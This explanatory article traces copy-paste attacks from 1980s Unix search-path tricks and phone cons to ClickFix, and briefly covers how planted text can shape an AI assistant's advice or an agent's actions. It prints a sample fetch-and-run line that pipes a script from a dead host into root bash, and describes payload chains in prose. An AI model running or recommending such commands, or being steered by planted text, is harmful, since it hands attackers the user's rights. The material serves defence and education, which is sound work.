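# Copy-paste attacks: how people are persuaded to run harmful commands and configurations, and how AI assistants are drawn in

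## What gives a pasted line of text control over a computer?

A copy-paste attack persuades a person to paste text into a computer and run it for the attacker's benefit. The text usually goes into a terminal, the window where a user types commands, but it can also go into a system dialog or a settings file. The attacker does not need a flaw in the software, because the computer is built to carry out instructions from a user who has the right to give them.

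Since 2023, the common criminal form of copy-paste attack has been ClickFix, in which a web page shows a fake check or error and gives a command as the remedy. The University of Florida's *ClickFix Attacks* uses "ClickFix" and "copy-paste attack" interchangeably, but the broader term is useful because the same trick works over the telephone, in a forum reply or in an AI assistant's answer.

A copy-paste attack involves an attacker, a channel, a victim and a machine. The attacker writes the text and a lure, a story that gives the victim a reason to paste it. The channel carries both to the victim, and its operator may know nothing about the attack. Apple now warns some Mac users when they paste into the terminal. The warning, reproduced in MacRumors' *macOS 26.4 Introduces New Security Feature for Terminal Commands* (2026), lists the usual channels as "websites, chat agents, apps, files, or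 a phone call". The victim has an account on the machine, which the attacker lacks. The text has the same effect on the machine whether the victim wrote it or copied it from a stranger.

MITRE's *User Execution*, part of a catalogue of attack methods that security teams use as a common reference, has a separate entry for "Malicious Copy and Paste". In the typical sequence given there, a person with a browser, email or document open starts a command program and pastes in one scrambled line. Shortly afterwards, the computer connects to an outside address.

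A terminal is one of several privileged environments, places where a computer runs text as commands with power over the system. Eric Lawrence, who works on Microsoft Defender, listed others in *Attack Techniques* (2024), a post on his blog text/plain. On Windows they include the Run dialog (opened with the Windows key and R), the command box in Task Manager, and the location bar in the window for choosing a file. Few people would think of that bar as a place to run programs.

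### Whose rights the text runs with

A shell is the program that reads typed or pasted commands and carries them out. Linux and macOS users mostly have bash or zsh, and Windows users have PowerShell or the older Command Prompt. Text on the clipboard does nothing until a shell runs it. Any program the shell starts normally has the rights of the signed-in user, so a pasted line can read, alter, delete or send away that user's files, although macOS asks before a program opens certain folders. The line can also set another program to start at every login.

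System-wide changes need administrator rights. Microsoft's *Understand UAC elevation prompts* gives installing applications and drivers, adding user accounts, and opening another user's folder as examples for Windows. On macOS and Linux, the equivalent rights belong to the all-powerful "root" account, and users usually borrow them with `sudo`. A user types `sudo` before a command and enters their own password, and the command runs as root. By default, `sudo` then skips the password for some minutes, so someone who has just used it may see no prompt.

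Windows handles elevation, the step up to administrator rights, through User Account Control. Even administrators ordinarily work with a standard user's rights. When a program requires more, Windows first refuses to start it and returns an error, according to Microsoft's *UAC Architecture*. A system service then picks up the request, asks the user for consent where the settings require it, and starts the program with full administrator rights. The prompt appears on a separate screen, which Microsoft's *How User Account Control works* calls the secure desktop. Only Windows' own processes can reach this screen, so ordinary malware can't click "Yes".

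That protects the prompt from other programs, but it does much less for a user who has already decided to approve it. According to an older edition of the same documentation, Microsoft's *How User Account Control Works*, the colour of the prompt depends on whether the program carries a trusted signature. PowerShell carries Microsoft's own signature, so its prompt has the same reassuring colour whether it is about to run the user's script or a criminal's. At the lowest notification setting, Windows approves administrators' requests automatically, without a prompt.

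Microsoft has since built a stricter scheme called *Administrator protection*. Windows creates administrator rights for one process at a time under a hidden separate account, requires a PIN, fingerprint or face scan each time, and destroys the rights when the process ends. Microsoft calls this a security boundary, meaning that it undertakes to fix any reported breach, whereas it describes User Account Control as more of an extra layer of defence. The German trade magazine IT-Administrator reports in *Administratorschutz in Windows 11 aktivieren* that the feature has shipped for recent versions of Windows 11 but is off by default. It stops malware from acquiring administrator rights silently, but a person who believes they are repairing their computer will still approve the request.

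The attacker often doesn't need administrator rights. Those rights protect the system from the user's programs, but not the user's own files and data, which are what a thief wants. A browser runs as the user and keeps its data in the user's folders. Browsers encrypt saved passwords, and some makers now try to tie the key to the browser itself, but the browser must be able to decrypt the passwords whenever the user signs in to a site, so another program running under the same account may be able to decrypt them too. Stealing a login session is even easier. After a login, a website gives the browser a cookie, a small file that stands in for the password on later visits, and a thief who copies it can often enter the account without the password or the code from the owner's phone.

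Malware that collects these things is called an infostealer. Krebs on Security (September 2024) described a web page with instructions to open the Run dialog, paste, and press Enter. The pasted text started PowerShell, which fetched and ran the infostealer Lumma Stealer. The University of Florida therefore tells victims to use another device to change every password they have used or stored on the affected one.

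Phones limit this kind of damage by isolating apps from each other. Desktop systems do so only in part. Apps from Apple's own store run in a sandbox that restricts their access to other apps' data, according to Apple's *Gatekeeper and runtime protection in macOS*, but a command in a terminal is not sandboxed this way. Microsoft has announced that Windows will ask users to approve each app's access to files, camera and microphone, Maruccia reported in *Windows 11's next security push borrows heavily from smartphones*.

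### One line, taken apart

Here is a made-up command of a very common kind. It is harmless, because the ending `.invalid` is reserved for addresses that lead nowhere.

```
curl -fsSL https://setup.example.invalid/fix.sh | sudo bash
```

`curl` is a small program that fetches whatever is at a web address. The four letters after the hyphen are settings. `f` makes curl stop if the server reports an error, so that the shell doesn't try to run the text of a "page not found" notice. `s` turns off the progress display and error messages, as the curl project's handbook explains, and the capital `S` turns the error messages back on. `L` makes curl follow redirects, so the script may come from a different address than the one in the line. The address comes next, and `fix.sh` is the name of the script, a text file of further commands.

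The vertical bar is a pipe, which feeds the output of the program on its left to the program on its right. According to the manual that Debian distributes, curl sends what it fetches to the terminal by default. The pipe diverts that output before it appears on the screen. Given no file to run, the shell `bash` reads commands from the pipe and runs them as they arrive. Putting `sudo` before `bash` runs them all with root privileges.

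Pasting this example would produce a "host not found" error and perhaps a password prompt. Bash would then receive no input and exit. If the address worked, whoever controlled the server at that moment would control the computer.

The line shows an address and that a script will run as root, but it doesn't show the commands in the script. Opening the address in a browser first is better than nothing, but a server can send one text to a browser and another to curl, or send something new an hour later. Attackers can also change the command that the victim pastes. *Analyzing full ClickFix attack chain part 1*, by the security company Stormshield, describes a ClickFix page that fetched the clipboard command from a server, so the operators could swap it without changing the page.

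The address can vanish as well. Base64 is an everyday encoding that rewrites any data in letters, digits and a few symbols. In base64 the address above becomes:

```
aHR0cHM6Ly9zZXR1cC5leGFtcGxlLmludmFsaWQvZml4LnNo
```

A standard tool can decode base64 text instantly, and the pasted command can include the instruction to do so. People can't read the encoded text by eye, so a user who has learned to check the domain name before trusting a link can't find one here. ReliaQuest, another security company, analysed a campaign in which the PowerShell text that victims copied was always in base64. Some attackers hide the command entirely. One fake verification page in the University of Florida's guide displays a harmless sentence about not being a robot, but its "Copy" button places something else on the clipboard.

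Some legitimate software is installed this way too, so the form of the command is not evidence of an attack. The makers of the Rust programming language and of Homebrew, a popular installer of software for macOS, have long given new users a one-line command that fetches a script with curl and hands it to a shell. In a forum discussion that fria opened in 2026 under the title *macOS 26.4 Brings New Terminal Security Feature to Stop Malicious Commands*, one participant complained that software vendors "who should know better" publish such lines. The complaint may be fair, but users have learned from these lines that this is what an installation looks like. Lawrence says 99.99% of pastes are trustworthy or harmless. The number is rhetorical, not measured, but he is surely right that most are.

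### Why download checks miss pasted text

Windows and macOS both inspect programs from the internet, and the inspection depends heavily on a label attached to the file. On a Mac the label is the quarantine mark, which Apple introduced in 2007. The Eclectic Light Company's *Quarantine and the quarantine flag* (2020) explains that this mark determines whether an app has to go through Gatekeeper's full first-run check. The check verifies that the app comes from a developer known to Apple, that Apple has scanned it for known malware, and that no one has altered it since. Gatekeeper also asks the user to approve opening the app for the first time.

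The Windows label is the Mark of the Web, a hidden note stored alongside a file that records the zone it came from (zone 3 is the internet). Lawrence explained how it works in a 2016 post on text/plain that he has kept up to date. When a user opens a marked program from the Windows desktop, SmartScreen looks up the program's reputation, Windows checks its signature, and any installed virus scanner can scan it.

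However, the program that downloads a file has to attach the label. Browsers do this, but curl does not on either macOS or Windows. The Eclectic Light Company's *Who decides to quarantine files?* (2025) confirms this for macOS 26 and adds that malicious software uses curl "almost universally" to download files without the label. On Windows, even a correctly labelled file triggers no check or prompt if a user starts it from the Command Prompt or PowerShell.

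The example command leaves no downloaded file to label. The script passes from the network into bash and exists only in memory. The only programs that visibly start are curl, sudo and bash, which the system already trusts. Stormshield found the same in its ClickFix case, where PowerShell ran the fetched script without writing it to disk.

The checks can still catch some attacks. Apple scans software for known malicious content when it first opens, "regardless of how it arrived on the Mac", and Smart App Control, an optional feature of Windows 11, also evaluates scripts. These can catch a payload, the harmful program that the pasted text fetches, if it is saved to disk as an ordinary program or resembles something already known. Apple writes in *Terminal and script protections* that attackers turned to persuasion as its anti-malware measures grew more effective, and macOS has included checks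 aimed at pasted text since version 26.4. Apple's praise of its own product calls for some caution, but the account fits how these attacks work. When checks focus on downloaded files, attackers benefit from persuading the computer's owner to run a command instead.

### The confused deputy

Computer scientists call a program a confused deputy when someone else induces it to misuse its authority. *The Confused Deputy*, a 1988 article by Norm Hardy, describes an accident about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers used a compiler, a program that translates code into a form the machine can run. The staff had given the compiler permission to write files in its own directory so that it could record usage statistics. The company's billing records were in the same directory. Customers could also name a file to receive debugging output, and one of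 them named the billing file. The customer didn't have permission to write to that file, but the compiler did. The operating system checked the compiler's permission and allowed the write, which destroyed the billing records.

Hardy concluded that the compiler had authority from two sources, the staff and the customer, and could not specify which one it was using for each file. He considered having the compiler refuse file names in other directories, but customers had good reasons to use those. He also considered having it refuse the billing file by name, but other files were sensitive too. His remedy was the capability, a single token that both identifies a file and permits its use. To make the compiler use the billing file, a customer would have needed a token for it, and had none. Rajani, Garg and Rezk later gave the first formal definition of freedom from such attacks in *On access control,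 capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*. They related it to information-flow integrity, roughly the requirement that untrusted input not influence what happens to protected data.

A person who pastes an attacker's command causes damage in the same way as the compiler in Hardy's example. The attacker, who has no rights on the machine, describes an act, the victim supplies the authority to perform it, and the system checks only that authority. The kinds of repair that failed for the compiler would also fail here. A rule against piping curl into a shell, for example, would block legitimate installers and still leave other routes open.

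Hardy's compiler mixed up two authorities, but the person at the keyboard has only their own. They use it for what they take to be their own benefit, and their mistake is about what the text will do. Capabilities would not prevent that mistake, since someone who trusts the lure will hand over a token as readily as a password. Capabilities could limit the loss, though, if a terminal held tokens only for the files that a job needs and none for the browser's data. Hardy remarked in passing that whoever runs a program yields their authority to it. He called this the tool of Trojan horses and described it as a "companion problem". The script that arrives through the pipe is a Trojan horse in this sense, and the copy-paste attack is a way of getting someone to run it.

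Unlike a compiler, a person can also stop, have doubts and ask a colleague. An AI agent, an assistant that runs commands itself, falls somewhere between the two. It is closer to Hardy's compiler when it reads a stranger's text while holding its user's permissions. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* quotes Red Hat and Microsoft applying Hardy's term, "confused deputy", to the servers that connect AI models to outside tools. In the quoted material, Microsoft warns that planted text could let an attacker run code on the machine.

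## How did earlier attackers get administrators and users to run things for them?

### A familiar name in the wrong directory

On a shared Unix machine of the 1980s, anyone with an account could write a program, but only the administrator, signed in as root, could change the whole system. An intruder with an ordinary account therefore wanted the administrator to run something as root. Duff (1989), in *Experience with Viruses on UNIX Systems*, described getting root to do this as the ultimate in system breaking, and credited F. T. Grampp and R. H. Morris with a discussion of how to get an unwary administrator to do it. Their article, "UNIX Operating System Security", appeared in AT&T's technical journal in October 1984, and O'Reilly's *Unix Security References* lists it as the original article on the subject.

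The usual method exploited the search path. When someone types `ls`, the command that lists files, the shell looks through a fixed series of directories and runs the first program it finds with that name. Many people put a dot, which stands for the current directory, at the start of the series. This was convenient for programmers testing their own work, but it also let a user leave a program called `ls` in their own directory for the administrator to run. If an administrator with this setting typed `ls` there, the user's program ran as root.

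A well-made planted script was hard to notice. O'Reilly's *Trojan Horses* gives an example that imitates `grep`, a command that searches text. The script runs the real `grep` first, so the output looks right. Then it checks whether root is running it, does its damage only in that case, and deletes itself.

Duff tried this on his colleagues at Bell Labs, where Unix was developed, using a small self-copying program he had written that did no deliberate damage. In September 1987 he looked up which directories people's shells searched before the system's own, and put an infected copy of `echo`, a command that prints text, into 48 of them. Only four of the 48 users noticed and asked about it. They were satisfied when he replied "Yes, I put it there" or "I'll tell you later", and nobody felt a need to remove the file. When he stopped the experiment eight days later, there were 466 infected files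 on 46 systems, largely because the lab's automatic software distribution had shipped an infected program to the other 45. It must have helped that Duff was a known colleague, but these users were about as expert as any group at the time.

At a trade show in 1986, the computer maker Gould offered a television to anyone who could break into UTX/32S, its hardened version of Unix, and a visitor named Darryl Wagoner won it. According to Gould's own account, preserved in the newsgroup thread *Slaying Gould dragon with a wooden horse*, Wagoner couldn't defeat the system's restricted environment, so he went after the "unwary-system-administrator" instead. The company blamed its booth staff, who had done a quick installation. A sceptical reader in the same thread quotes the two main mistakes Gould admitted: the administrators had put the current directory (".") first in their search path, and they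 had run a user's program.

In the argument that followed the break-in, Dave Cornutt thought that a better search path would not have saved Gould, because Wagoner could have just asked an administrator to run his program. He recalled an old student trick of complaining about a weird error in a homework program and begging the administrator to run it. Reed (1986) was less sure, writing that he would have real qualms about running a stranger's program as root but might not even think about running `ls`. Stewart (1986) suggested combining the two by mailing root to say that some command doesn't work in one's home directory and asking for help. This lure gives the administrator a plausible reason to go to the booby-trapped directory and type the familiar name.

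It took administrators two attempts to fix the search path. They first moved the dot from the start of the list to the end, so that the shell would always find the real `ls` first. *Classic Unix Security Problems* (Dominus, 2005) explains why this helped but wasn't enough. Root sometimes mistypes `ls` as `sl`, and because no real program has that name, the shell continues down the list and runs an attacker's `sl`. The better rule was to leave the dot out of root's path. Chambers, another reader of the Gould thread, had known that the dot shouldn't come first but hadn't realized it might be dangerous anywhere in the list. Duff added that nobody's path should include a directory that other people can write to.

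None of this helps against the homework request. Duff also discussed a proposal to limit which files a program could touch. As Duff noted, its inventors had observed that users can't reasonably approve every file access, since the questions would never stop.

### Orders by mail and telephone

By 1991 intruders were sending the instructions straight to ordinary users. CERT/CC, the computer emergency team at Carnegie Mellon University, published two warnings that year about messages that could appear to come from a site's administrator. In one sample, the supposed administrator cites "security faults" and orders the reader to change their password to `systest001` at once by typing `passwd` at the shell prompt, adding that they can change it back in ten minutes at most. The attack needed no malicious program, because `passwd` was the system's genuine tool and users had every right to change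 their own passwords. The intruder only had to sign in during those ten minutes.

The other sample came from a supposed company called OmniCore, which wanted help testing a game, TurboTetris. Readers were supposed to type the location of a program that the intruder had already placed on the machine. The program would prompt them to log on again ("use your real password") and then mail the name and password to a remote site. CERT/CC admitted that this might look trivial to experienced users but wrote, without giving a number, that "MANY users have fallen for these tricks".

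CERT/CC told users to check any such request with their system administrator before acting on it. It told administrators never to mail a request for a password change that specifies the new password. If administrators follow this rule, users can tell that any request that does so is fake, even if the sender's name is convincingly forged.

An attacker on the telephone could adjust his story as he went. *Approaching Zero* (Mungo and Glough, 1992) describes a fifteen-year-old in Indiana, nicknamed Fry Guy, who in 1989 wanted the unlisted number of a credit bureau's computer. He rang the telephone company's operations section as "Bob Johnson, Indiana Bell tech support" and asked the employee who answered to pull up a file. She sounded uncertain, so he dictated the keys to press, one by one, and she then read him the number. He used it, with an account code and password he had talked out of a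 shopkeeper, to get credit card details, and had $687 wired to a friend, then $432 the next day. The dialogue reads like a reconstruction, so its exact wording deserves little weight. But as in a copy-paste attack, he supplied the text to someone who had the terminal and the right to use it.

Mitnick and Simon's *The Art of Deception* (2002), the best-known book on such calls, is a weaker source than its fame suggests because its anecdotes are "purely fictional" unless otherwise stated. One exception is the story of Stanley Rifkin, which is based on published reports that don't fully agree. In 1978 Rifkin was working for a contractor at Security Pacific National Bank in Los Angeles. He read the day's transfer code off a slip of paper in the wire room, then called the room from a pay phone in the lobby, posing as "Mike Hansen" of the international department. He gave the clerk the office number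 and code she asked for, but he didn't have the settlement number she asked for next. He promised to call back, got the number from another department by posing as a wire-room employee, and called again. The clerk then sent $10.2 million towards Switzerland.

The bank did check the caller three times, but each check tested only whether he knew something, which a patient stranger could have found out. In *Information Security Technology?...Don't Rely on It*, Winkler and Dealy describe a test attack on a company, which they began by getting the names of employees and officials from public databases and an office number from a local telephone directory. The usual remedy is to hang up and call the colleague back on a number from the company's own list. This tests where the caller is rather than what he knows, but it can fail if the attacker can reroute telephone lines, as Fry Guy could.

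A reviewer of Mitnick's book for the magazine CSO (2002) objected that technology could do more than Mitnick allowed. The reviewer argued that most attackers can't write their own malware, and that a good antivirus program stops a clerk from downloading or running malware already in circulation. The objection was fair, but it did not cover a person who damages the computer by hand.

### The virus that wasn't there

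In the spring of 2001, computer users around the world began deleting SULFNBK.EXE, a Microsoft utility in Windows for backing up and restoring long file names, because an email told them to. The email claimed that a virus was hiding in the file and would strike on 1 June, and it told readers to search their hard drives for the file and delete it. The first report came from Brazil, in Portuguese, on 17 April, according to a Symantec notice that a subscriber quoted in the mailing list post *SERIOUS (no, it isn't)* (2001).

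The two obvious ways to check the message did not expose it as a hoax. Bekker (2001) pointed out in *Hoax Serves as Reminder to Users* that the utility had shipped with Windows 95 and 98, so many people who looked for it found it, which seemed to confirm the warning. The copy that Snopes collected also tells readers in capitals not to rely on their antivirus software, claiming that McAfee and Norton can't detect the virus because it doesn't become one until 1 June, so a clean scan would not reassure anyone who believed the message.

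The message also asked readers to contact everyone they had emailed. On 2 June a subscriber to an academic list passed on the steps, saying he had followed them "succesfully". Alzugaray Treto (2001), in *Virus alert*, corrected him the same day. People were still forwarding the message in December, when Klevnäs (2001), in *HOAX FW*, pasted Microsoft's instructions for restoring the file into a reply on another list.

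A year later the same thing happened with JDBGMGR.EXE, a Microsoft file for Java programmers whose icon was a small bear. Schulman (2002), in *Microsoft Debugger Registrar for Java (Jdbgmgr.exe) Is Not a virus*, reproduced a version of the warning that began "I found the little bear in my machine". The virus supposedly lay dormant for 14 days. One recipient, in the thread *VIRUS ALERT* (2002), wrote that she had checked her hard drive and found the file, so she had "no doubt passed it around", and she was now warning her contacts. Bekker (2002), in *Hoax Circulating About Java File*, reported that the antivirus company Sophos had received thousands of inquiries in a week, but nobody knows how many people deleted the file without asking.

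The harm was modest. Leyden (2002) warned that Java programs might fail to run, while Microsoft's *FAQ from Security Newsgroups* told people who had deleted the file not to bother restoring it, since they would probably never need it. Snopes left open whether the SULFNBK message was a prank or an honest mistake, so there may not have been an attacker. Both alarms had some basis in fact. Symantec noted that a virus could infect SULFNBK.EXE like any other program, and Leyden traced the second scare to a real virus, Magistr-A, which could send out infected copies of JDBGMGR.EXE.

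The remedies were repair articles, publicity, and a general rule from Microsoft not to follow instructions in unsolicited email from sources one doesn't know and shouldn't trust. The rule is good, but it would have stopped few of these deletions, because the warnings came mostly from friends and colleagues who thought they were true.

### Chat commands and ordinary error logs

In the 1990s, the main public chat network was Internet Relay Chat, and mIRC was a popular Windows program for using it. mIRC treated a line that began with a slash as a command, and its scripting language could write files and start other software. Strangers in a channel offered newcomers a line to paste, promising special powers in the channel or a hidden feature. The line installed a script that could let the stranger control the victim's chat program, and the script often posted the same offer to others. Help channels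 warned against pasting unknown lines, and mIRC's developer added settings that lock the riskiest commands.

A cruder version appeared on Linux forums, where jokers answered beginners' questions with a command that deletes every file. Moderators of the Ubuntu forums posted a standing notice about such answers. Programmers also changed the delete command that most Linux systems use, so that it refuses to erase the entire file system unless the user adds an explicit override. This safeguard covers only the most obvious form of the joke, but honest users rarely run into it.

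From the late 2000s, telephone fraudsters made a business of impersonating support staff and raising false alarms. The caller claimed to be from Microsoft or "Windows support" and had the victim open Event Viewer, the program that displays Windows' log of errors and warnings. Every healthy Windows machine logs plenty of both, but the caller presented them as signs of infection. Callers also often read aloud a long identification code that a standard Windows command prints, claiming that it was unique to the victim's computer and so proved the call was genuine. The code is the same on every copy of Windows.

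As with SULFNBK.EXE, the victim runs the check personally and sees real output from their own machine. They don't know what normal output looks like, so the caller interprets it for them. The victim then installs a legitimate remote-control program and pays for a repair that does nothing or makes things worse. The US Federal Trade Commission took six such operations to court in 2012. Microsoft has told customers for years that it doesn't make unsolicited support calls. Like CERT/CC's ban on dictated passwords, this is a promise about how the real organisation behaves.

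### Self-XSS and the console that refuses a paste

Cross-site scripting (XSS) is a flaw in a website that lets an attacker's code run inside the site's pages. Attackers who can't find such a flaw can ask the user to put the code there instead, which is called self-XSS. This became common on Facebook around 2011.

At first, victims pasted the code into the browser's address bar, usually because they had been promised a virtual reward or a way into somebody else's account. If the text began with `javascript:`, the browser ran it as JavaScript, the programming language of web pages, inside whatever page was open. If that page was Facebook, the code could post, send messages and spread the offer to friends as the signed-in user. Browser makers closed this route in 2011. The Chrome team proposed stripping the `javascript:` prefix from anything pasted into the bar, and Firefox's developers moved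 to cut off the code's access to the open page.

Attackers then sent people to the developer console, a panel in which web developers type code to test a page. Victims had to press a key combination and paste the code into an unfamiliar window, but the code could do the same things once it ran. The site's owner can't fix this, because the attack doesn't rely on a flaw in the site. Facebook began printing a large "Stop!" in the console and explaining that anyone told to paste something there was the target of a scam. In 2014 it also tried switching the console off for some users, which annoyed developers.

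From 2014 on, browser makers responded by adding a barrier. When a person who hasn't used the console before tries to paste into it, Firefox blocks the paste and shows a warning about scams until the user types `allow pasting`. Chrome adopted the same phrase roughly a decade later. Developers only have to type it once, so the inconvenience is small, and everyone else sees the warning when it is relevant. The barrier's weakness is that a user can type the phrase without reading the warning, so a scammer can include it as one more step in the instructions. Apple later added a similar warning for text pasted into its terminal.

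The damage from self-XSS is also limited, usually to one account on one site, because the code runs with the web page's rights, whereas a command pasted into a terminal has the user's rights over everything in their folders.

### When the clipboard holds something else

In all these cases a careful reader could at least have seen the text. In 2013 the security researcher Jann Horn put up a demonstration page that took this away. It showed an ordinary command for downloading source code, but the page's formatting hid extra text in the middle of the line, out of sight. A visitor who selected the line with the mouse selected the hidden part as well. In 2016 Dylan Ayrey published a variant, under the name pastejacking, that needed no hidden text. A small script on the page noticed the copy command and put its own text on the clipboard. A harmless made-up case would look like this:

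```
Shown on the page:     echo "good morning"
Pasted by the user:    echo "good night"
```

Line breaks made clipboard substitution more dangerous. Shells of the time treated a line break in pasted text as pressing Enter, so the command ran before the user could see that it was the wrong one.

Terminals and shells addressed that part of the problem with a feature called bracketed paste. The terminal marks where pasted text begins and ends, and the shell holds the text on the command line until the user presses Enter. Zsh turned this on by default in 2015, and bash did so at the end of 2020. Pasting into a plain text editor first also lets the user read the text before running it. Browser makers still let web pages control what gets copied, because online word processors and every "Copy" button depend on it. Horn's and Ayrey's pages were demonstrations aimed at people who would read a command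 before running it, while ClickFix pages now use the same ability on people who mostly won't.

### Should anyone pipe a script into a shell?

Much of the worry about clipboard substitution concerned software developers, who routinely copy installation commands from web pages. Developers had already been arguing for years about the most common such command, which downloads a script with curl and pipes it straight into bash.

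One purely technical complaint from critics is that bash runs the script as it arrives, so it may run only half the script if the connection drops. A command to delete a temporary folder could delete something else if it is cut off in the middle of the folder's name. Careful publishers have solved this. Rust's installer, for example, wraps its work in a function and calls it only on the last line, so almost nothing happens until the whole script has arrived.

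The other complaints are harder to answer. The script leaves no copy to examine after an accident. Reading it in a browser first isn't a reliable check, because a 2016 demonstration showed that a server could infer from the timing of a download that a shell was running the script as it arrived, and change the text. Critics also say that Linux distributions have a better method. Their maintainers sign each package and the user's machine verifies the signature, so an attacker who breaks into one web server can't forge it.

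Defenders of install scripts reply that the user is about to run the vendor's software anyway, and a dishonest vendor could do harm through the program as easily as through the script. An encrypted connection already protects the script in transit. Few people verify signatures by hand, and if the vendor publishes the key on the same website, whoever takes over the site can replace both the key and the signature. A script is also easier to read than an ordinary installer, and it works on many versions of Linux for which nobody has made a package.

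The defenders are mostly right that the pipe adds little risk compared with downloading an installer from the same site and double-clicking it. Their case is weaker when the alternative is a signed package from a distribution. It also assumes that the user has correctly identified the vendor, whereas a copy-paste attack works on someone who hasn't. The criticism about habit still holds, because honest one-line commands have taught users to expect them. Many projects now offer signed packages alongside the one-line command, which helps the users who choose them.

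### Where advice from an AI assistant fits

The forged mail from root and the call from "Indiana Bell tech support" relied on impersonating someone entitled to give orders. An AI assistant can recommend a harmful command without anyone being impersonated, because the user has opened the genuine product and already trusts it. A closer precedent is the friend who forwarded the SULFNBK warning. The recipient knew the friend, who meant no harm, and neither of them could see where the text came from. An assistant isn't sincere in the way a friend is, but the effect is the same, and advice to distrust strangers fails in both cases.

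Fry Guy and the sender of the TurboTetris message both had to invent a reason for the victim to act, and an invented reason can sound odd. But a person who asks an AI assistant how to free up disk space already has a real one, which makes the attacker's task easier. Microsoft's rule about unsolicited instructions doesn't apply, since the user asked for them.

Attackers still rely on the rights of the person they deceive, and this has changed little since 1986. The Gould administrator had root, Rifkin's clerk could move money, the Facebook user had an open session, and the person who pastes an assistant's command has their own account and perhaps an administrator password. The exception is an agent that runs the command itself, because it uses the user's rights but the user may never handle the text.

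Assistant users can check a command more easily than earlier victims could in some ways, but less easily in others. Fry Guy's victim had a pushy caller on the line and could hardly ask him to explain each key. A user can ask an assistant what every part of a command does, spend an hour on the answer, and choose not to paste anything. However, the explanation comes from the same source as the command, so planted text that shaped one may have shaped the other. In 1991, CERT/CC advised asking a different person. The hoaxes may also have been easier to look up than an assistant's answer. Everyone received much the same email, so the subscriber in *SERIOUS (no, it isn't)* only had to type the file name into Google to find Symantec's warning. An assistant can word its advice differently for each user, so there may be no earlier victim's complaint to find.

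## How does ClickFix work, and how much damage does it do?

ClickFix shows people a fake check or error and tells them to run a command to resolve it. Researchers found the first known version in October 2023. It combined the false alarm used in telephone support scams with the clipboard switching that Horn and Ayrey had each demonstrated earlier. Unlike a telephone scammer, a web page can target thousands of people at once.

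### How people end up on the page

Many victims arrive through an advertisement. In September 2026 attackers took over HBO Max's verified Reddit account and ran 108 advertisements from it in 48 hours, according to Hudson Rock's *HBO Max ads on a compromised Reddit account* (2026). Some offered a nonexistent HBO Max application for the Mac. The download button on the landing page displayed instructions for pasting a command into the terminal. Of the 108 advertisements, 46 were related to streaming, 47 led to supposed AI tools for developers, who are used to installing software with a pasted line, and 15 led to a supposed disk cleaner.

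Advertising platforms review what they publish, so attackers try to show reviewers something different from what victims see. *From W-2 to BYOVD*, by the security company Huntress, describes a commercial service that does this for $299 to $999 a month and also blocks security scanners. The campaign Huntress was investigating didn't use ClickFix, but the operation behind the Reddit advertisements also checked its visitors before deciding what to send them.

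Attackers who hack an existing website don't have to pay to advertise it, and it already has visitors who trust it. Recorded Future's *GrayCharlie Hijacks Law Firm Sites in Suspected Supply-Chain Attack* (2026) describes a group that inserts code into sites built with WordPress, a popular publishing program. Visitors to the affected law firms' sites saw fake browser updates or ClickFix pop-ups. Red Code's *How Attackers Are Adapting ClickFix Into Longer Attack Chains* (2026) mentions a dental practice whose site showed a fake check only after the visitor clicked something, such as a consent notice.

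Attackers can use stolen passwords to hack more websites and run ClickFix attacks from them. In July 2026, researchers traced a ClickFix campaign on part of the website of Artlist, which licenses music and video footage, to WordPress credentials that an infostealer had taken earlier.

### One attack, step by step

In August 2026 Microsoft described a campaign it calls TerminalFix, which began on hacked websites. The real page appeared for a moment before a fake Cloudflare check covered it. Cloudflare shields many websites from unwanted traffic, and it does ask some visitors to tick a box to show that they are human, a test called a CAPTCHA. The fake check had Cloudflare's logo, the box and a spinning wheel.

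When the visitor clicked, the page silently copied a PowerShell command to the clipboard, then displayed instructions to open Windows Terminal or PowerShell and paste it. Most people have passed dozens of these checks without thinking, so visitors may not have questioned an odd extra step.

The command cleared the window and printed a cyan message that Cloudflare's verification was starting. Meanwhile, it downloaded and unpacked an archive and started a program from it. Finally, it printed "I am not a robot" in green with an identification number. The victim saw what looked like a successful check and had no obvious reason to call the IT department.

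The archive contained a genuine Windows program, signed with a valid signature, and a malicious library (a file of shared code for other programs to load). Windows looks for some libraries in a program's own folder before it looks in the system's, so the program loaded the attacker's library instead of Microsoft's. The malicious code then ran inside a process that security software was likely to treat as safe. Security specialists call this sideloading.

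Next, the malicious code downloaded three pictures whose pixel values encoded more software. It reassembled this software on the disk, then deleted the pictures. It scheduled the whole process to restart at every login and every 60 minutes. Then it listed the administrators on the organisation's network and tested which servers responded, including those whose names suggested databases or backups. The script had versions for English, Spanish and German systems.

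In the last step, the malware downloaded an ordinary copy of Python, a programming language, from its official site and used it to run a small script without a visible window. The script opened an encrypted connection from the victim's computer to the attackers. A firewall that only blocks incoming connections doesn't stop this, because the connection starts inside the network. The attackers could then reach any machine that the victim's computer could reach, and their traffic looked like someone using a website.

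Microsoft warns that attackers with this kind of access typically go on to steal data and deploy ransomware. It did not observe either step in the TerminalFix chain, so this campaign is evidence of serious access, but the damage from it is unknown.

### Run dialog, terminal or file manager

Most earlier ClickFix pages told people to open the Run dialog. The instructions can be short because the dialog opens with two keys and has little more than a single line for text. It shows only part of a long command, usually the end, so attackers can put a reassuring phrase there. Mishcon de Reya's *From clipboard to compromise* (2025), a law firm's summary of research by Huntress, describes a page that filled the victim's screen with a fake Windows Update. When the progress messages finished, the page asked the victim to open the Run dialog.

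One pasted line is enough because it only has to start a chain of programs and scripts. Huntress' *Someone's Hands Are on Your Keyboard Then Your Whole Network* describes a case from May 2026 in which the pasted line used one built-in Windows tool to start another, which fetched a small script from the web. That script used curl to download an installer and ran it without showing a window. The first programs to start were all part of Windows, which makes them hard to block outright.

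Microsoft says one reason TerminalFix switched to a terminal is that terminals accept longer scripts with several lines. Cybersecurity Help's *ClickFix campaign abusing Windows Terminal to deploy Lumma Stealer* adds two more reasons in its account of a February 2026 campaign. Administrators use Windows Terminal for ordinary work, so the request can look more legitimate, and some detection tools concentrate on the Run dialog. But an office worker who has never seen a terminal may well stop when asked to open one, though nobody seems to have measured how many do.

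A variant called FileFix uses the file manager, which is more familiar. A researcher published it in June 2025, and criminals took it up within weeks. The page claims that someone has shared a document and asks the visitor to open a file window and paste the document's location into the address bar. The pasted text is a command that ends in something like a file path, so the victim thinks they are finding a document.

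### Where attackers keep the script

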